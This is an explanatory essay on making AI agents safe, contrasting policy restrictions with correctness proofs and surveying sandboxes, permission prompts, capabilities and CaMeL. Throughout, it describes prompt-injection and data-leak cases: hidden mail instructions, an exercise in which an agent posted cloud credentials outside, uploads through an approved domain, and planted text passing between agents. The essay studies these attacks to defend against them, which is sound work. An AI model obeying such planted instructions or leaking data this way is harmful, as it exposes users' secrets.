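# Limiting the harm an AI agent can do and verifying that its code does what was intended

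## What the two guarantees are

An AI agent is a language model connected to tools, so its output causes actions such as sending an email, changing a flight booking or editing a file. Some agents act by writing short programs that call those tools. Running such a program carries two risks. It may do damage, for instance by deleting files or passing private data to a stranger, and it may fail to do what the user asked. Computer science has older methods for addressing each risk. Sandboxes, access rights and type systems limit what a program can do, while tests and proofs check that it does what was intended.

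These methods support two guarantees. A restriction guarantee means that the effects of any code the agent writes stay within a stated policy. A correctness guarantee means that a particular program meets a stated specification.

### How an agent acts by writing code

In the older arrangement, the model writes one request at a time in JSON, a text format for structured data. The request names a tool and its arguments, and the surrounding software runs the tool and returns the result to the model. *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents* (2024) was an early proposal to let the model write Python instead. In the paper's prompts, the JSON version limits the model to one tool at a time, while the code version permits loops and if-statements around the calls.

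*The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of finding the circumference of a circle of radius 7 and the area of a square of side 5. A model that uses JSON makes two tool calls, while a model that writes code produces one script that calls both functions and prints both results. Code helps more on longer jobs, because a script can move data from one tool to the next without sending all of it through the model. Anthropic's engineering post *Code execution with MCP* discusses the Model Context Protocol, a standard way of connecting models to tools. It says that for a two-hour sales meeting, the model could otherwise have to process an extra 50,000 tokens (the word fragments in which models process text).

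Patel and colleagues found that 11 of 14 models did at least as well on 309 function-calling tasks when they wrote code as when they made JSON calls. The other three were OpenAI models that often wrote line breaks incorrectly, which crashed their scripts. Patel and colleagues also say that JSON remains the dominant interface in deployed systems, but they name only one production system as evidence.

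Code helps with both guarantees because the whole program exists as text before any of it runs, so other software can read it, refuse it or confine it. In *Guardians of the Agents*, Meijer uses this in a safety method where the agent must first produce its complete workflow, and nothing runs until a checker has passed it. The drawback is that a program with branches and loops can behave in many ways, and the checker has to cover them all.

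An agent writes two kinds of program. Agent code is a program the agent writes and runs to carry out a request, such as a script that compares documents. Delivered code is a program the agent writes for others to run later, often with different permissions. A patch to a payroll system is delivered code, and it may run next month under an account that can read every salary. Limits on the agent's workspace constrain agent code but not the patch once someone installs it. *Intent Formalization* (Lahiri, 2026) describes developers who accept AI-written code with little or no review, a practice called vibe coding. Their delivered code goes into use with neither guarantee unless someone supplies one.

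### Restriction: every program the agent could write

A trace is the sequence of effects that one run of a program produces. In *Soteria* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026), the trace of a tool-using agent lists each tool call with its arguments and result. A policy is a rule, usually fixed before the task, about which effects and data flows are acceptable. One of the paper's rules for an airline's agent requires it to check that the passenger has not flown any of the flights on a reservation before cancelling that reservation. Every trace either obeys this rule or breaks it, so one can treat a policy as the set of traces that obey it.

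Some policies concern information flow, which is the movement of data, or anything computed from it, from a source to a destination. Meijer's example is a rule that nothing from the mail-reading tool may end up in the body of a message to an outside address. The rule allows both reading mail and sending it, and forbids only the flow of data from the first to the second.

With *L* for the set of programs that the agent could submit and Π for the policy, the restriction guarantee is:

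*for every program p in L, and every trace t that p can produce, t belongs to Π.*

*Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) proves a guarantee of this form, covering every program, for a small agent framework called PocketFlow. It represents the AI as a procedure with no body, which may return any action of the declared type. A verifier, a program that checks a proof that code meets its specification on all inputs, must then confirm that the framework follows the policy whatever actions arrive, in any order. The policy confines file reads to one directory and tool calls to an approved list, and it caps the number of steps. The proof does not depend on the model's training or motives, but it does depend on the set of actions being narrow. If one of them were "run any shell command", the guarantee would cover only what can be proved about shell commands, which is very little.

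Another approach uses access rights called capabilities. A capability is an unforgeable value that a program must hold to use a resource. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that relies on the type checker of the programming language Scala. In this system, a file-system object is a capability. Code must hold the object to open any file, and the object gives access only to files under one directory.

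Every guarantee has a trusted base, the components that must work as assumed for the guarantee to hold. Odersky and colleagues trust the Scala compiler, their own library, the runtime and, when an agent needs help with secret text, a separate local model. Moon and Varshney trust the verifier, the compiler and the policy, and they assume that every outside effect passes through the interface they modelled. Neither trusted base includes the model that writes the code or picks the actions.

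### Correctness: this program and this task

A specification is a checkable statement of what a program must do for a given task. It commonly has a precondition, which marks out the permitted inputs, and a postcondition, a statement that must be true when the program finishes. For one fixed program *p* the correctness guarantee is:

*for every input x that satisfies the precondition, the result of running p on x satisfies the postcondition.*

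"Result" here includes whatever the program has changed in the world. Meijer gives the example of a request to delete two files, foo.txt and bar.txt. A program that deletes every text file on the disk would satisfy the obvious postcondition, that neither file exists afterwards. To exclude that program, the specification needs a frame condition, which lists what must stay unchanged.

Lahiri describes three levels of evidence for correctness. Tests check the specification on the finitely many inputs somebody thought to try, so passing them gives some evidence, but only about those inputs. Runtime checks evaluate the specification on each execution and catch an error only when it happens. A proof covers all possible inputs, and only a proof delivers the guarantee as stated above.

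### Where the two differ

| | Restriction guarantee | Correctness guarantee |
|---|---|---|
| Who writes the rule | Usually an administrator or the owner of the tools | The user, or someone interpreting the user |
| When | Before the task, often once for many tasks | Along with the task |
| Does it depend on the task? | Little | Entirely |
| Must it hold for a hostile author? | Yes, for any program the author submits | It concerns only the program at hand |

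*LogAct* (2026) describes an agent system built around a shared log and is an example of the first row. An outside person, such as an administrator, supplies the safety conditions, and the design does not depend on any assumption about the user's request, which may be unsafe. A policy of this kind can stay in use for a long time. For example, He and colleagues wrote an airline's rules as 24 formulas in a few hours, and the formulas apply to every task in that domain. Correctness has no such reusable set of rules, because two requests to the same airline agent call for different outcomes.

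Both guarantees depend on the task, but to different degrees. Odersky and colleagues combine a reusable library with a short list, specific to each request, of what the agent may access. A person reviews that list before the agent starts. Tighter policies need more tailoring to the request.

The same paper assumes that the cloud-hosted model may be helping the attacker, so the restriction has to withstand code written to defeat it. A correctness proof has to cover only one program, and if the proof is sound, the author's motives make no difference. Tests offer less protection against a hostile author, because someone who knows the tests can write a program that passes them and fails in other cases.

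### One request, four outcomes

In the main scenario used by Odersky and colleagues, a user asks an agent to compare two sets of confidential contracts and summarise what has changed. The agent may read the contract database, compare documents, ask an isolated model for a summary and write to one output file. The policy is that contract text goes nowhere else. A reasonable specification is that the summary reports every changed clause and no change that did not occur. An outcome is "harmless" if the agent stays within the policy and "right" if the result meets the specification, so the request can end in four ways.

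| Outcome | The contracts request | Airline tasks, no enforcement | Airline tasks, with enforcement |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harmless and right | The summary is accurate and nothing leaks | 34% | 60% |
| Harmless and wrong | The summary misses a new liability clause; nothing leaks | 30% | 40% |
| Harmful and right | The summary is accurate; the program also sends the contracts to an outsider | 14% | 0% |
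| Harmful and wrong | The summary misses the clause and the contracts leak | 22% | 0% |

The percentages come from a different setting, in which He and colleagues ran the model GPT-5.4-mini once on each of 50 airline customer-service tasks. They report that without enforcement it completed 48% of the tasks, completed 34% without a violation, and avoided violations in 64%; the other shares are calculated from these by subtraction. All four outcomes are common, and 7 of the 24 completed tasks involved a broken rule. The last column shows results for their full system, which blocks forbidden calls and also gives the agent a checked plan to follow, so blocking alone does not account for the rise in success. With the full system, violations fall to zero, but the agent still fails 20 of the 50 tasks.

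Harm is hardest for a user to notice when the agent's answer is right. In an attack that Meijer describes, a user asks for a summary of her mail, and one message in the inbox contains instructions to send a summary to an outside address and keep quiet about it. The agent complies, then shows her an ordinary-looking summary, so checking the answer more carefully would not reveal the leak.

Odersky and colleagues distinguish safety from correctness for agents. They list correctness among their non-goals, say that an agent under their restrictions may still produce wrong results, and call correctness "orthogonal to our safety guarantees". They don't argue for this, though the logical case is not hard to make. He and colleagues likewise define a successful run by two criteria, utility and conformance. Moon and Varshney exclude the truthfulness of what an agent writes from the scope of their proof.

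*Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (Qu, Xu and colleagues, 2026) instead defines security as a form of correctness. An agent is secure when its execution faithfully reflects the user's intent, much as a compiler is correct when the compiled program behaves as the source code prescribes. The paper's strongest example is an agent that reviews papers. A submission contains the claim that leading experts consider it the best work in its field, and the agent scores it too highly. The agent makes no forbidden tool call, so a policy on tool calls would not prevent the error.

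That failure counts as harmless and wrong in the table above. To prevent it, Qu and colleagues propose the formal condition that *J*(*q*, *d* ⊕ δ) = *J*(*q*, *d*), where *J* is the agent's decision, *q* the user's query, *d* the data, and δ any irrelevant text that an attacker adds. An agent that gives every paper the same score satisfies this condition. The condition guards against manipulation but does not prevent ordinary mistakes, so even under this broader definition of security a user would want separate assurance that the answer is right.

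### Two gaps

Both guarantees compare a program with a written rule, and the rule can be wrong. A policy that restricts the agent may not cover the real harm. *Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies* (2026) acknowledges in its threat model that if a condition is badly specified, the system will enforce it faithfully and still misbehave in the world. In the contracts example, the policy allows the agent to write its summary to one file. If half the company can read that file, the agent exposes confidential terms without violating the policy. The harmless and wrong outcome may still harm, in the everyday sense, a client who relies on a bad summary when signing.

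Careful authors run into this gap too. When He and colleagues audited their results, they found rules they had encoded wrongly or left out, although they had worked clause by clause from written policy documents. Their count of zero violations therefore refers to the corrected formulas. In one variant of Moon and Varshney's automated pipeline, a generated safety rule referred to a field that the program never filled in. This made the rule true in every run, so the verifier accepted it even though it protected nothing.

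The corresponding gap for correctness lies between the specification and what the user meant. Lahiri gives the example of a request to remove duplicates from a list of numbers. Given 1, 2, 3, 2, 4, one reader expects 1, 2, 3, 4, while another expects 1, 3, 4, with every copy of the repeated number removed. Each reading yields a precise specification, and a program can provably meet the one the user did not intend. Lahiri points out that only the user can say which is right. An administrator can fix a gap in a policy for all later tasks, but what the user meant has to be established again for each request.

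## Why neither guarantee implies the other

The two guarantees are independent because of what each one states. On the airline tasks, agents often stayed within the rules and failed, or succeeded while breaking a rule. Those results alone don't settle whether the guarantees are independent, because agents might have completed the tasks under a better policy, and a better specification might have prevented the harm.

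### A program that does nothing

Suppose a policy forbids an agent from sending mail outside the company. An agent that sends no mail obeys it. More generally, a program that stops at once produces only the empty trace, which has no effects. It satisfies every policy that allows the empty trace, but it does not complete any task that requires an action. So no such policy can guarantee that the task gets done. Adding prohibitions does not help, because an empty trace contains nothing to prohibit.

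*Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (2025) uses this fact in its proof. It describes a procedure that returns a tool call only if the call keeps the trace within the rules. If a fixed number of attempts produces no acceptable call, the procedure returns a dummy call that has no effect and that no rule mentions, so the trace stays compliant. The theorem would also hold for an agent that made only dummy calls.

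Some policies require actions as well as forbidding them. On Toolathlon, a benchmark of tool-use tasks, He and colleagues enforce a rule that an agent must read back any file it has written. An agent that does nothing satisfies this rule, because it has written no files. A rule that every run must record a verdict would exclude a program that does nothing, but not one that records the wrong verdict. A policy that excluded every unsatisfactory program would have to describe the finished task, which would make it a specification.

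In practice, an agent that breaks no rules can still fail most of its tasks. He and colleagues' system broke no rules on Toolathlon with any of the four models they tried, but its success rate was only 9.3% to 18.6%. The tasks are hard even without enforcement. The best unguarded agent completed 30.2% of them, and only 11.6% without a violation. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026), a survey of such systems, likewise concludes that blocking unsafe actions does not automatically lead an agent to complete the task safely.

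Restricting an agent can still help it succeed. *Reason Less, Verify More* (2026) reports higher task success when checks blocked certain forbidden actions, because those actions would have silently corrupted the data and made the task unrecoverable. The agent still had to find the right action itself.

### Deleting two files

Meijer's request to delete foo.txt and bar.txt shows the opposite failure. The agent's tool, delete_file, accepts a pattern of file names. The agent could call it twice, but a single call with the pattern `*.txt` makes a shorter program. Take a folder that holds foo.txt, bar.txt, notes.txt and budget.xls, and write *F* for the set of files present at the end. The obvious postcondition is:

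*foo.txt ∉ F and bar.txt ∉ F.*

After the single call, only budget.xls remains, so the postcondition holds. This is equally simple to prove, because the tool's contract (its own specification) states that every file matching the pattern will be gone, and both names match. The program therefore meets its specification, although it has deleted notes.txt and would violate any policy against deleting files the user did not name.

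Meijer prints his frame condition as part of the tool's contract. With *F*₀ for the set of files present before the call, it reads:

*for every file f that does not match the pattern, f ∈ F exactly when f ∈ F₀.*

He writes that the `*.txt` program then fails to verify. The printed condition does not achieve this alone, because notes.txt matches the pattern and so falls outside its protection. The specification of the task needs a frame condition too:

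*for every file f other than foo.txt and bar.txt, f ∈ F exactly when f ∈ F₀.*

Now the verifier must show that notes.txt survives if it was there at the start. The proof fails because the tool's contract implies that notes.txt does not survive. If the user's folder contains no other text files, a test there would pass, but the proof would still fail because it has to cover every possible starting folder.

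The tool's frame condition matters for a different reason: without it the verifier cannot accept the good program.

| Where the frame condition appears | Two calls, one per file | One call with `*.txt` |
|---|---|---|
| Nowhere | Rejected | Accepted |
| Tool's contract only | Accepted | Accepted |
| Task's specification only | Rejected | Rejected |
| Both | Accepted | Rejected |

The first row is the worst case. Without a frame condition, the contract for the second call guarantees only that bar.txt is gone. It does not rule out the call restoring foo.txt, so the verifier rejects the careful program and accepts the destructive one.

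Meijer traces the difficulty to the frame problem, which McCarthy and Hayes described in *Some Philosophical Problems from the Standpoint of Artificial Intelligence* (1969). The problem is that a logical description of what an action changes implies nothing about what it leaves unchanged. People fill in the rest from common sense, but a verifier uses only what someone has written down.

### Safety and liveness

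An older distinction in the theory of program verification resembles the one between the two guarantees. *Proving the Correctness of Multiprocess Programs* (Lamport, 1977) divides the properties one must prove about a program into safety properties, which state that something will not happen, and liveness properties, which state that something must happen. In its main example, one process puts messages into a buffer with room for *b* of them and another takes messages out. The safety property is that the number of messages in the buffer always lies between 0 and *b*. To prove it, one finds conditions that imply it, then checks that they hold at the start and that no step by either process can make them false. Two processes that never took a step would also satisfy this property.

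Correctness includes both safety and liveness properties, so restriction and correctness do not correspond to safety and liveness. Lamport's first example of a safety property is partial correctness, which means that if the program starts with a permitted input and stops, its answer is right. His first example of a liveness property is termination, which means that the program eventually stops. In a later retrospective, Lamport explains that he was generalising these two properties, which Robert Floyd had proved for ordinary programs in 1967. He needed broader ones because few programs made of several processes are supposed to stop.

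Alpern and Schneider (1985), in *Defining Liveness*, gave exact definitions for a property *P*, understood as a set of traces:

- *P* is a safety property if every trace outside *P* has a finite beginning that no continuation can bring back into *P*.
- *P* is a liveness property if every finite beginning has some continuation that lies in *P*.

Partial correctness is a safety property because a program violates it by stopping with a wrong answer, and once stopped, the program cannot correct that answer. Total correctness also requires termination, which is a liveness property. The two guarantees therefore do not correspond to safety and liveness. A specification that requires total correctness contains both kinds of property, and He and colleagues' read-back rule is a liveness property in a policy.

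Alpern and Schneider also proved that every property of traces is the intersection of a safety property and a liveness property. Given a property *P*, let *P̄* be the set of traces whose every finite beginning can be extended to a trace in *P*. This is the smallest safety property that includes *P*. Let *L* be the set of traces that are in *P* or outside *P̄*. The intersection of *P̄* and *L* is then *P*. *L* is a liveness property because every finite beginning can be extended to a trace in *L*. If a beginning can be extended to a trace in *P*, that trace is also in *L*. If it can't, all its extensions are outside *P̄* and therefore in *L*.

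The deletion task can be split into a safety property, "the program never deletes any other file", and a liveness property, "both named files are eventually gone". The idle program satisfies only the safety property, and the `*.txt` program satisfies only the liveness property.

### What a run-time monitor can enforce

A run-time monitor watches a program's steps and stops the program before a step that would break the policy. In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider proved that such monitors can enforce only safety properties. The monitor evaluates each run in isolation and must reject a bad run after finitely many steps. It also cannot let a program pass through a forbidden stage, even if later steps would correct it, because the run might end there. So if a finite trace is unacceptable, every continuation of it must be unacceptable too. Together, these conditions imply Alpern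 and Schneider's definition of safety.

By the last condition, if a run obeys an enforceable policy, so does every run made by stopping it early, including the run with no steps (the empty trace). The do-nothing argument therefore applies to every policy that such a monitor can enforce, except one that forbids all runs. In Schneider's example, a seller has received payment. A monitor can prevent the seller from doing anything except deliver the service, but no monitor of this kind can guarantee delivery, because the seller may do nothing.

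A monitor also cannot enforce some safety properties. For example, a rule that nobody may wait more than a fixed number of seconds for a resource is a safety property, because a violation is visible at a definite moment. The monitor cannot enforce this rule because time keeps passing even after it stops the program. If the rule counts the program's steps instead of seconds, the monitor can enforce it.

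A monitor can help with partial correctness if the system requires permission to declare the task complete. *TraceGrant* (2026) separates the decision to allow a tool call from the decision to declare the task complete. It records what each call did, checks the postconditions it can observe, and withholds the declaration until the agent has met its obligations. This check can prevent a false report of success when an observable postcondition has not been met, but it cannot make the agent finish the task.

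Schneider's limit applies to monitors that only observe a running program and stop it. It does not apply to compilers and theorem provers, because they examine the program's text and can reason about runs that have not happened. He and colleagues use this kind of analysis to enforce the read-back rule, checking before execution that every successful path through the agent's plan includes the required read. An earlier system, CaMeL, checks policies during execution and cannot naturally express policies about what must happen, so *CaMeLoT* (2026) moves those policies to the planning stage too.

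*What Can Be Enforced?* (2026), which applies the classical theory to tool-using agents, notes that monitors can also enforce more if they alter a program's actions. For instance, a monitor could itself read back each file the program writes. But to ensure that an arbitrary task gets completed this way, the monitor would have to know how to do the task.

### Secrecy concerns more than one run

The formula given earlier for the restriction guarantee tests each trace separately, so it cannot express secrecy. Suppose an agent may read salaries and book meeting rooms. One program reads an employee's salary and books room A if it is high and room B if it is low, so anyone who knows the program can learn about the salary from the booking. A second program reads the salary and always books A, and a third reads it and always books B. Neither of these reveals anything about the salary, so a policy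 that tests traces one at a time must accept all their traces. These include every trace the first program can produce, so the policy must also accept the first program, even though its bookings reveal whether the salary is high or low.

Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, introduced a wider class of properties to cover such cases. A hyperproperty judges the whole set of traces that a system can produce. One example is observational determinism, which they take from earlier work:

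*for every two runs of the program, if they look the same to an outsider at the start, they look the same to that outsider throughout.*

A violation consists of two runs, neither of which is a violation by itself. Every information-flow policy that Clarkson and Schneider examined was a hyperproperty rather than a property of single traces, though they caution that no definition of information flow is generally accepted.

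Ordinary verification methods can still check a rule about two runs. One technique joins the program to a copy of itself with renamed variables, gives both copies the same public inputs and possibly different secrets, and proves that their public outputs match. The proof fails for the room-booking program when one copy receives a high salary and the other a low one. Clarkson and Schneider extended the method to rules whose violations can be shown with any fixed number of runs.

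A monitor that observes only the current run has to enforce a policy stricter than secrecy. In Schneider's example, the policy forbids sending any message after reading a file. This keeps the file's contents out of later messages, but also blocks messages that have nothing to do with the file.

### When a specification does entail a policy

Let *S* be the set of traces that a specification allows. A program meets the specification if all its traces lie in *S*. If every trace in *S* also lies in the policy Π, a program that meets the specification obeys the policy too:

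*if traces(p) ⊆ S and S ⊆ Π, then traces(p) ⊆ Π.*

*S* lies inside Π only if the specification covers every effect that the policy is about. The deletion specification does not, even with both frame conditions, because it describes only which files exist at the end. A program could satisfy it and still mail the contents of foo.txt to a stranger before deleting the file, blank out notes.txt without removing it, or delete notes.txt and then restore it from a backup. The specification therefore has to constrain the intermediate steps as well as the final state.

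The specification must also cover every run to which the policy applies. If the precondition is that both files exist, the specification doesn't restrict what the program does in a folder where bar.txt is missing, so a program could wipe that folder and still count as correct. Partial correctness only restricts runs that finish, so a program that leaks data and then runs forever also counts as partially correct.

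A stronger specification for the task would require the program, from any starting folder, to end with foo.txt and bar.txt gone and to have no effect at any step other than deleting them. Any program that meets this specification also obeys policies against sending mail and deleting other files. But if a policy protects bar.txt because of a lawsuit, a program can meet the specification only by breaking the policy, so the specification must include the policy's limit, for example by exempting files under legal protection.

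Anyone who writes a rule permitting "only" certain effects must know what all the possible effects are. Schneider points out that a rule about sending messages works only if its definition of "send" covers every way a message can leave the system, and some of those ways may be hard to find.

Secrecy needs one more condition, because a program can leak a secret while producing only traces that a harmless system could also produce. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that unpredictably outputs 0, 1 or a secret bit. Its possible outputs are the same whatever the secret is. A second system that always outputs the secret bit produces only traces that the first could produce, but it reveals the secret. A specification that lets an agent book any free room has the same weakness, since the program that chooses by salary satisfies it. The specification therefore has to state secrecy as a relation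 between runs, in a form that still holds when a program produces only some of the permitted traces. Observational determinism has this form.

Even then, proving a program correct shows only that this program obeys the restrictions. The restriction guarantee covers every program the agent writes, so correctness proofs imply it only if the system refuses to run any program that lacks one, as in Meijer's method.

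## Restricting an agent while its code runs

A run-time restriction checks a program's actions just before they take effect. The actual file name, address or message exists by then, so nobody has to predict what the program will do. The check can stop only the actions that pass through it, and it can use only the information available at that point. For instance, a file-system sandbox has the path of each file but no record of what the user asked for.

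### Operating-system sandboxes

A sandbox runs code under rules that the operating system, or a layer beneath it, enforces on requests to open files, start processes or use the network. The code may be hostile and may be in any language, because the check happens outside it. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes three versions:

- In the chat product claude.ai, code runs on the company's servers in a container whose files last for one session.
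- Claude Code, a programming agent that works on the developer's own machine, uses the sandbox features of macOS and Linux. Commands may read files, may write only inside the project folder and have no network access by default.
- Claude Cowork, an agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own operating system. Only the folder the user selected and a settings folder are visible there, and credentials stay outside.

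In an internal exercise in February 2026, a researcher tricked an employee into starting Claude Code with a prompt that looked like routine setup instructions. One step was to read the employee's cloud credentials and post them to an outside address, which Claude did in 24 of 25 attempts. Because the instruction came from the user, defences that look for departures from the user's wishes had nothing to detect. Anthropic concludes that only limits on file access and network traffic would have stopped the attack.

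Sandboxes let through anything that uses an approved route. Claude Cowork has to contact Anthropic's servers, so its network filter allowed that domain. In an attack that outside researchers reported, a file in the user's folder contained hidden instructions and the attacker's access key. Claude read other files in the folder and uploaded them to the attacker's account on the same servers. The filter allowed the upload because the domain was approved. Anthropic now treats allowing a domain as granting access to every function reachable there. It fixed the flaw with a proxy that accepts only requests carrying the session's own token.

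Restrictions can also fail because a check runs too late. A project folder could contain a settings file that defined a command, and Claude Code ran that command at startup, before asking whether the user trusted the folder. The operating system itself can also have flaws. Moon and Varshney cite Copy Fail, a Linux kernel flaw that let programs gain extra privileges and had existed for nearly a decade. In 2026, restrictions repeatedly failed where enforcement was incomplete.

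### Permission rules and user approval

Permission rules determine which kinds of action need a person's approval. When Claude Code first appeared, it could read files freely but had to ask before it wrote a file, ran a shell command or used the network. The person can base her decision on what she wanted the agent to do, which is information a sandbox lacks.

Anthropic found that users approved about 93% of these prompts. Most of the requests may have been harmless, so the figure doesn't measure how many approvals were mistakes. Anthropic also observed that people pay less attention to each prompt as they see more of them. Experienced users turned on automatic approval about twice as often as new users, but they also interrupted the agent more often.

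Adding the sandbox cut permission prompts by 84%, because most commands inside it no longer needed approval. The company has also automated some approvals, and says the automatic mode catches about 83% of overeager actions before they run. By that figure, roughly one in six still run, so the mode reduces risk but doesn't guarantee that the agent stays within its restrictions.

Users also need expertise to judge the commands they are asked to approve. A developer can probably tell that `find . -name "*.tmp" -exec rm {} \;` deletes every file ending in .tmp in the current folder and its subfolders, but many office workers cannot, which is why Claude Cowork relies on a fixed boundary.

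### Policy checks on tool calls

A policy monitor checks each tool call against a set of rules and allows or refuses it. It works with the tool's name and arguments, which are often more informative than the requests an operating system receives. For example, "send this message to this address" is easier to judge than "write these bytes to a network connection".

*Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) gives a short policy for a tool that edits files. By default, the policy denies everything except network traffic. It allows writing in the workspace folder if the user asked to edit files, and it forbids network traffic if the session contains sensitive data. The same tool call can therefore be allowed in one session and forbidden in another.

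Such rules fail if the tool does more than its description states. In one of the paper's examples, a tool described as only writing a file also sends its own name and the file's size to a metrics service. A monitor that relied on the description would allow the call even during work on secret code.

To close this hole, Adam and colleagues analyse the tool's code in advance and list every kind of effect it could have. The analysis cannot predict which file a call will write to, because the path arrives only with the call. So the tool's developer wraps each effect in a small sandbox that receives the policy for that call. The analysis then confirms that no effect bypasses these sandboxes and that no instruction alters the policy on its way to them. When the tool runs on somebody else's server, the client also needs evidence that the server is running the analysed code. In the full design, security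 hardware provides that evidence.

### How permitted steps combine into a leak

Suppose a user asks an agent to set up a new project by copying a configuration file from an older one. The file contains a private key for an online service. Later she asks the agent to publish the project on GitHub, a site for sharing code. The agent, having copied the file, runs `git push` and uploads the key to GitHub with the rest of the project. Adam and colleagues observed this with the model Claude 4.5 Haiku. Nobody attacked the agent, and both tools worked as described.

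Copying a file between the user's own folders is harmless by itself, and she asked the agent to publish the project. A rule that judges each call separately must either allow both steps, which allows the leak, or always forbid one of them. Blocking network access, for example, would stop the agent from publishing any project. The same problem arises whenever an agent is allowed to both read a secret and call a network service.

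A monitor that remembers earlier calls can do better. Schneider's rule against sending anything after reading a file would prevent this leak, but it would also stop the agent from publishing harmless files. Adam and colleagues instead issue a new policy before each call. If the copied file contains a key, the policy for `git push` can cut off network access, or it can hide only that file from the command so that the rest of the project is still pushed.

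They tested the method by recording agent sessions and replaying them under four arrangements. Each of the three scenarios had a version in which the agent had only the intended effects and a version in which something went wrong.

| Arrangement | Intended versions allowed | Faulty versions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| No protection | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
| One fixed sandbox around all tools | 2 of 3 | 1 of 3 |
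| Code analysis alone | 2 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
| Code analysis with a sandbox for each effect | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

This small demonstration suggests that software can enforce the right policy once somebody has it. It assumes a source of correct policies, and in the GitHub scenario the experimenters also told the agent whether the file was sensitive, so the results don't show that software can work out which files are sensitive.

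### Object capabilities and the confused deputy

Access rules usually allow or deny a request based on who is making it. This goes wrong when a program with extensive rights acts on behalf of someone with fewer, which security researchers call the confused deputy problem. In the standard example, a compiler has permission to write to a billing file. A user without that permission tells the compiler to save its output under the billing file's name. The system checks only the compiler's permission, so it allows the write, and the output overwrites the billing records.

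An agent is a deputy of this kind, since it works with its user's access while reading text written by strangers. In the Claude Cowork attack, the user had given the agent permission to read the files, but the instruction to upload them came from the attacker, and no check compared the two sources.

Object capabilities address the problem by combining a resource's name with the right to use it. The user passes the compiler an object that lets it write to one file, instead of passing a file name. She has no such object for the billing file, so she cannot pass one.

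This works only if the language offers no other way to reach the resource. An ordinary Python script can open any path that its user account can, regardless of which objects it was passed. The per-call policy that Adam and colleagues pass to a tool looks like a capability, but a carelessly written tool could write to the disk without consulting it, so they also need the code analysis. Odersky and colleagues use a compiler for that check.

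Capabilities limit which resources a program can reach, but they do not by themselves control how data moves between those resources. A script that holds one object for reading a folder and another for sending mail to a colleague can still send the folder's contents to that colleague.

### CaMeL: following data to each tool call

CaMeL, a system that Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, controls the flow of data directly. It defends against prompt injection, in which text that an agent was only supposed to read contains instructions that the agent then obeys. *CaMeLoT*, a later extension of the system, gives an example in which an agent has to find Bob's email address in a group chat and send him a message about a meeting. In outline, the plan is:

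```
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
email    = ask_second_model("Extract Bob's email", messages)
send_direct_message(email, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

A first model writes this program from the user's request alone, before the chat is fetched. A second model reads the chat and returns an address. It has no tools, so an instruction hidden in the chat cannot make it delete a channel or send a file. An interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls. It also labels every value with its sources and with the people who may read it. A value computed from other values inherits their labels.

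Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short Python function that receives the arguments with their labels and returns "allow" or "deny". This second defence matters because an attacker can still write in the chat that Bob has a new address, which leaves the plan unchanged but puts the attacker's address in `email`. A policy that accepts recipients only from trusted sources blocks the message. Similarly, CaMeL's policy for changing a password requires the new password to come from the user.

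Papers on CaMeL call these labels capabilities. Unlike an object capability, which gives access to a resource, a label describes a piece of data. In the example of the published key, if the label names only the user as a permitted reader, the policy can refuse to publish the key no matter how many steps came between reading and publishing it. This works only if the label stays attached to the key through those steps. If a shell command copies the key from one file to another, the interpreter can't track it unless the tools record where it went.

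### What CaMeL costs and what it prevents

AgentDojo, a benchmark for prompt injection, has 97 ordinary tasks and 35 attack goals across office work, Slack, banking and travel. *CaMeLoT* reports a run of CaMeL on the 97 tasks with the model Claude Haiku 4.5 and no attacks. CaMeL completed 49. Of the other 48, its policies blocked at least 17, and at least 22 failed because the plan did not accomplish the task. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) likewise reports that turning on the policies halves CaMeL's success on the banking tasks.

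Separating the two models protects against many attacks even without policies. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) divided AgentDojo's tools among several cooperating agents and tested five models on 949 attacked tasks each. Adding CaMeL to every agent, with no data policies, reduced the average attack success rate from 12.9% to 0.2%. The effect varied widely by model. The rate for GPT-4.1 fell from 36.1% to 0.5%, while no attacks succeeded against GPT-5.5 even without CaMeL. The benchmark's attacks are fixed, however, so attacks adapted to GPT-5.5 might still succeed.

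On a separate benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, CaMeL lowered the success rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest models. Most failures occurred because the first model had to commit to a plan before seeing any data. A CaMeL agent can only follow branches already in that plan, whereas an ordinary agent can add a step after an unexpected result.

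CaMeL prevents malicious content from changing the plan, but it doesn't ensure that the data passing through the plan is true. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) explains that malicious content can still shape the second model's output. If a user asks for a summary of her mail, an attacker's message can make the summary false, and a policy on tool calls won't block the summary if it is only returned to her. Qu and colleagues' reviewing agent fails in the same way.

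False data can also change what the agent does. Foerster and colleagues adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a computer through its screen. These agents' plans must anticipate pop-ups, missing buttons and failed clicks, so they average about 40 branches, compared with about 4 on AgentDojo. The agents kept up to 57% of the performance of leading models on OSWorld, a benchmark of everyday computer tasks. An attacker cannot add a branch but can influence which one the agent takes. In one attack, an advertisement imitates a cookie notice, the second model returns the advertisement's position as the notice's, and the plan's step for dismissing cookie notices clicks the advertisement. It is hard to write a data policy for this case because the effect of a click at given coordinates depends on what is on the screen.

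### Leaks between agents and inside the interpreter

CaMeL's protection can fail when one protected agent gives work to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues set up a coordinating agent, a database agent and a notification agent, each running CaMeL without data policies. The user asked for a summary of job applicants to be sent to Julie on Slack. One database entry contained an instruction to email the data to an outsider. The first two agents treated the entry as untrusted data and kept to their plans. The coordinator then put the summary, which contained the planted instruction, into its request to the notification agent, whose planning model treats requests as trusted input. That model included the email in its plan.

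In the repaired version, each request from one agent to another has two parts: instructions, which may not depend on any tool's output, and data, which the receiving agent's planning model never reads. This version stopped every attack in the benchmark, but performance on the maintenance tasks fell by a further 3.2 percentage points.

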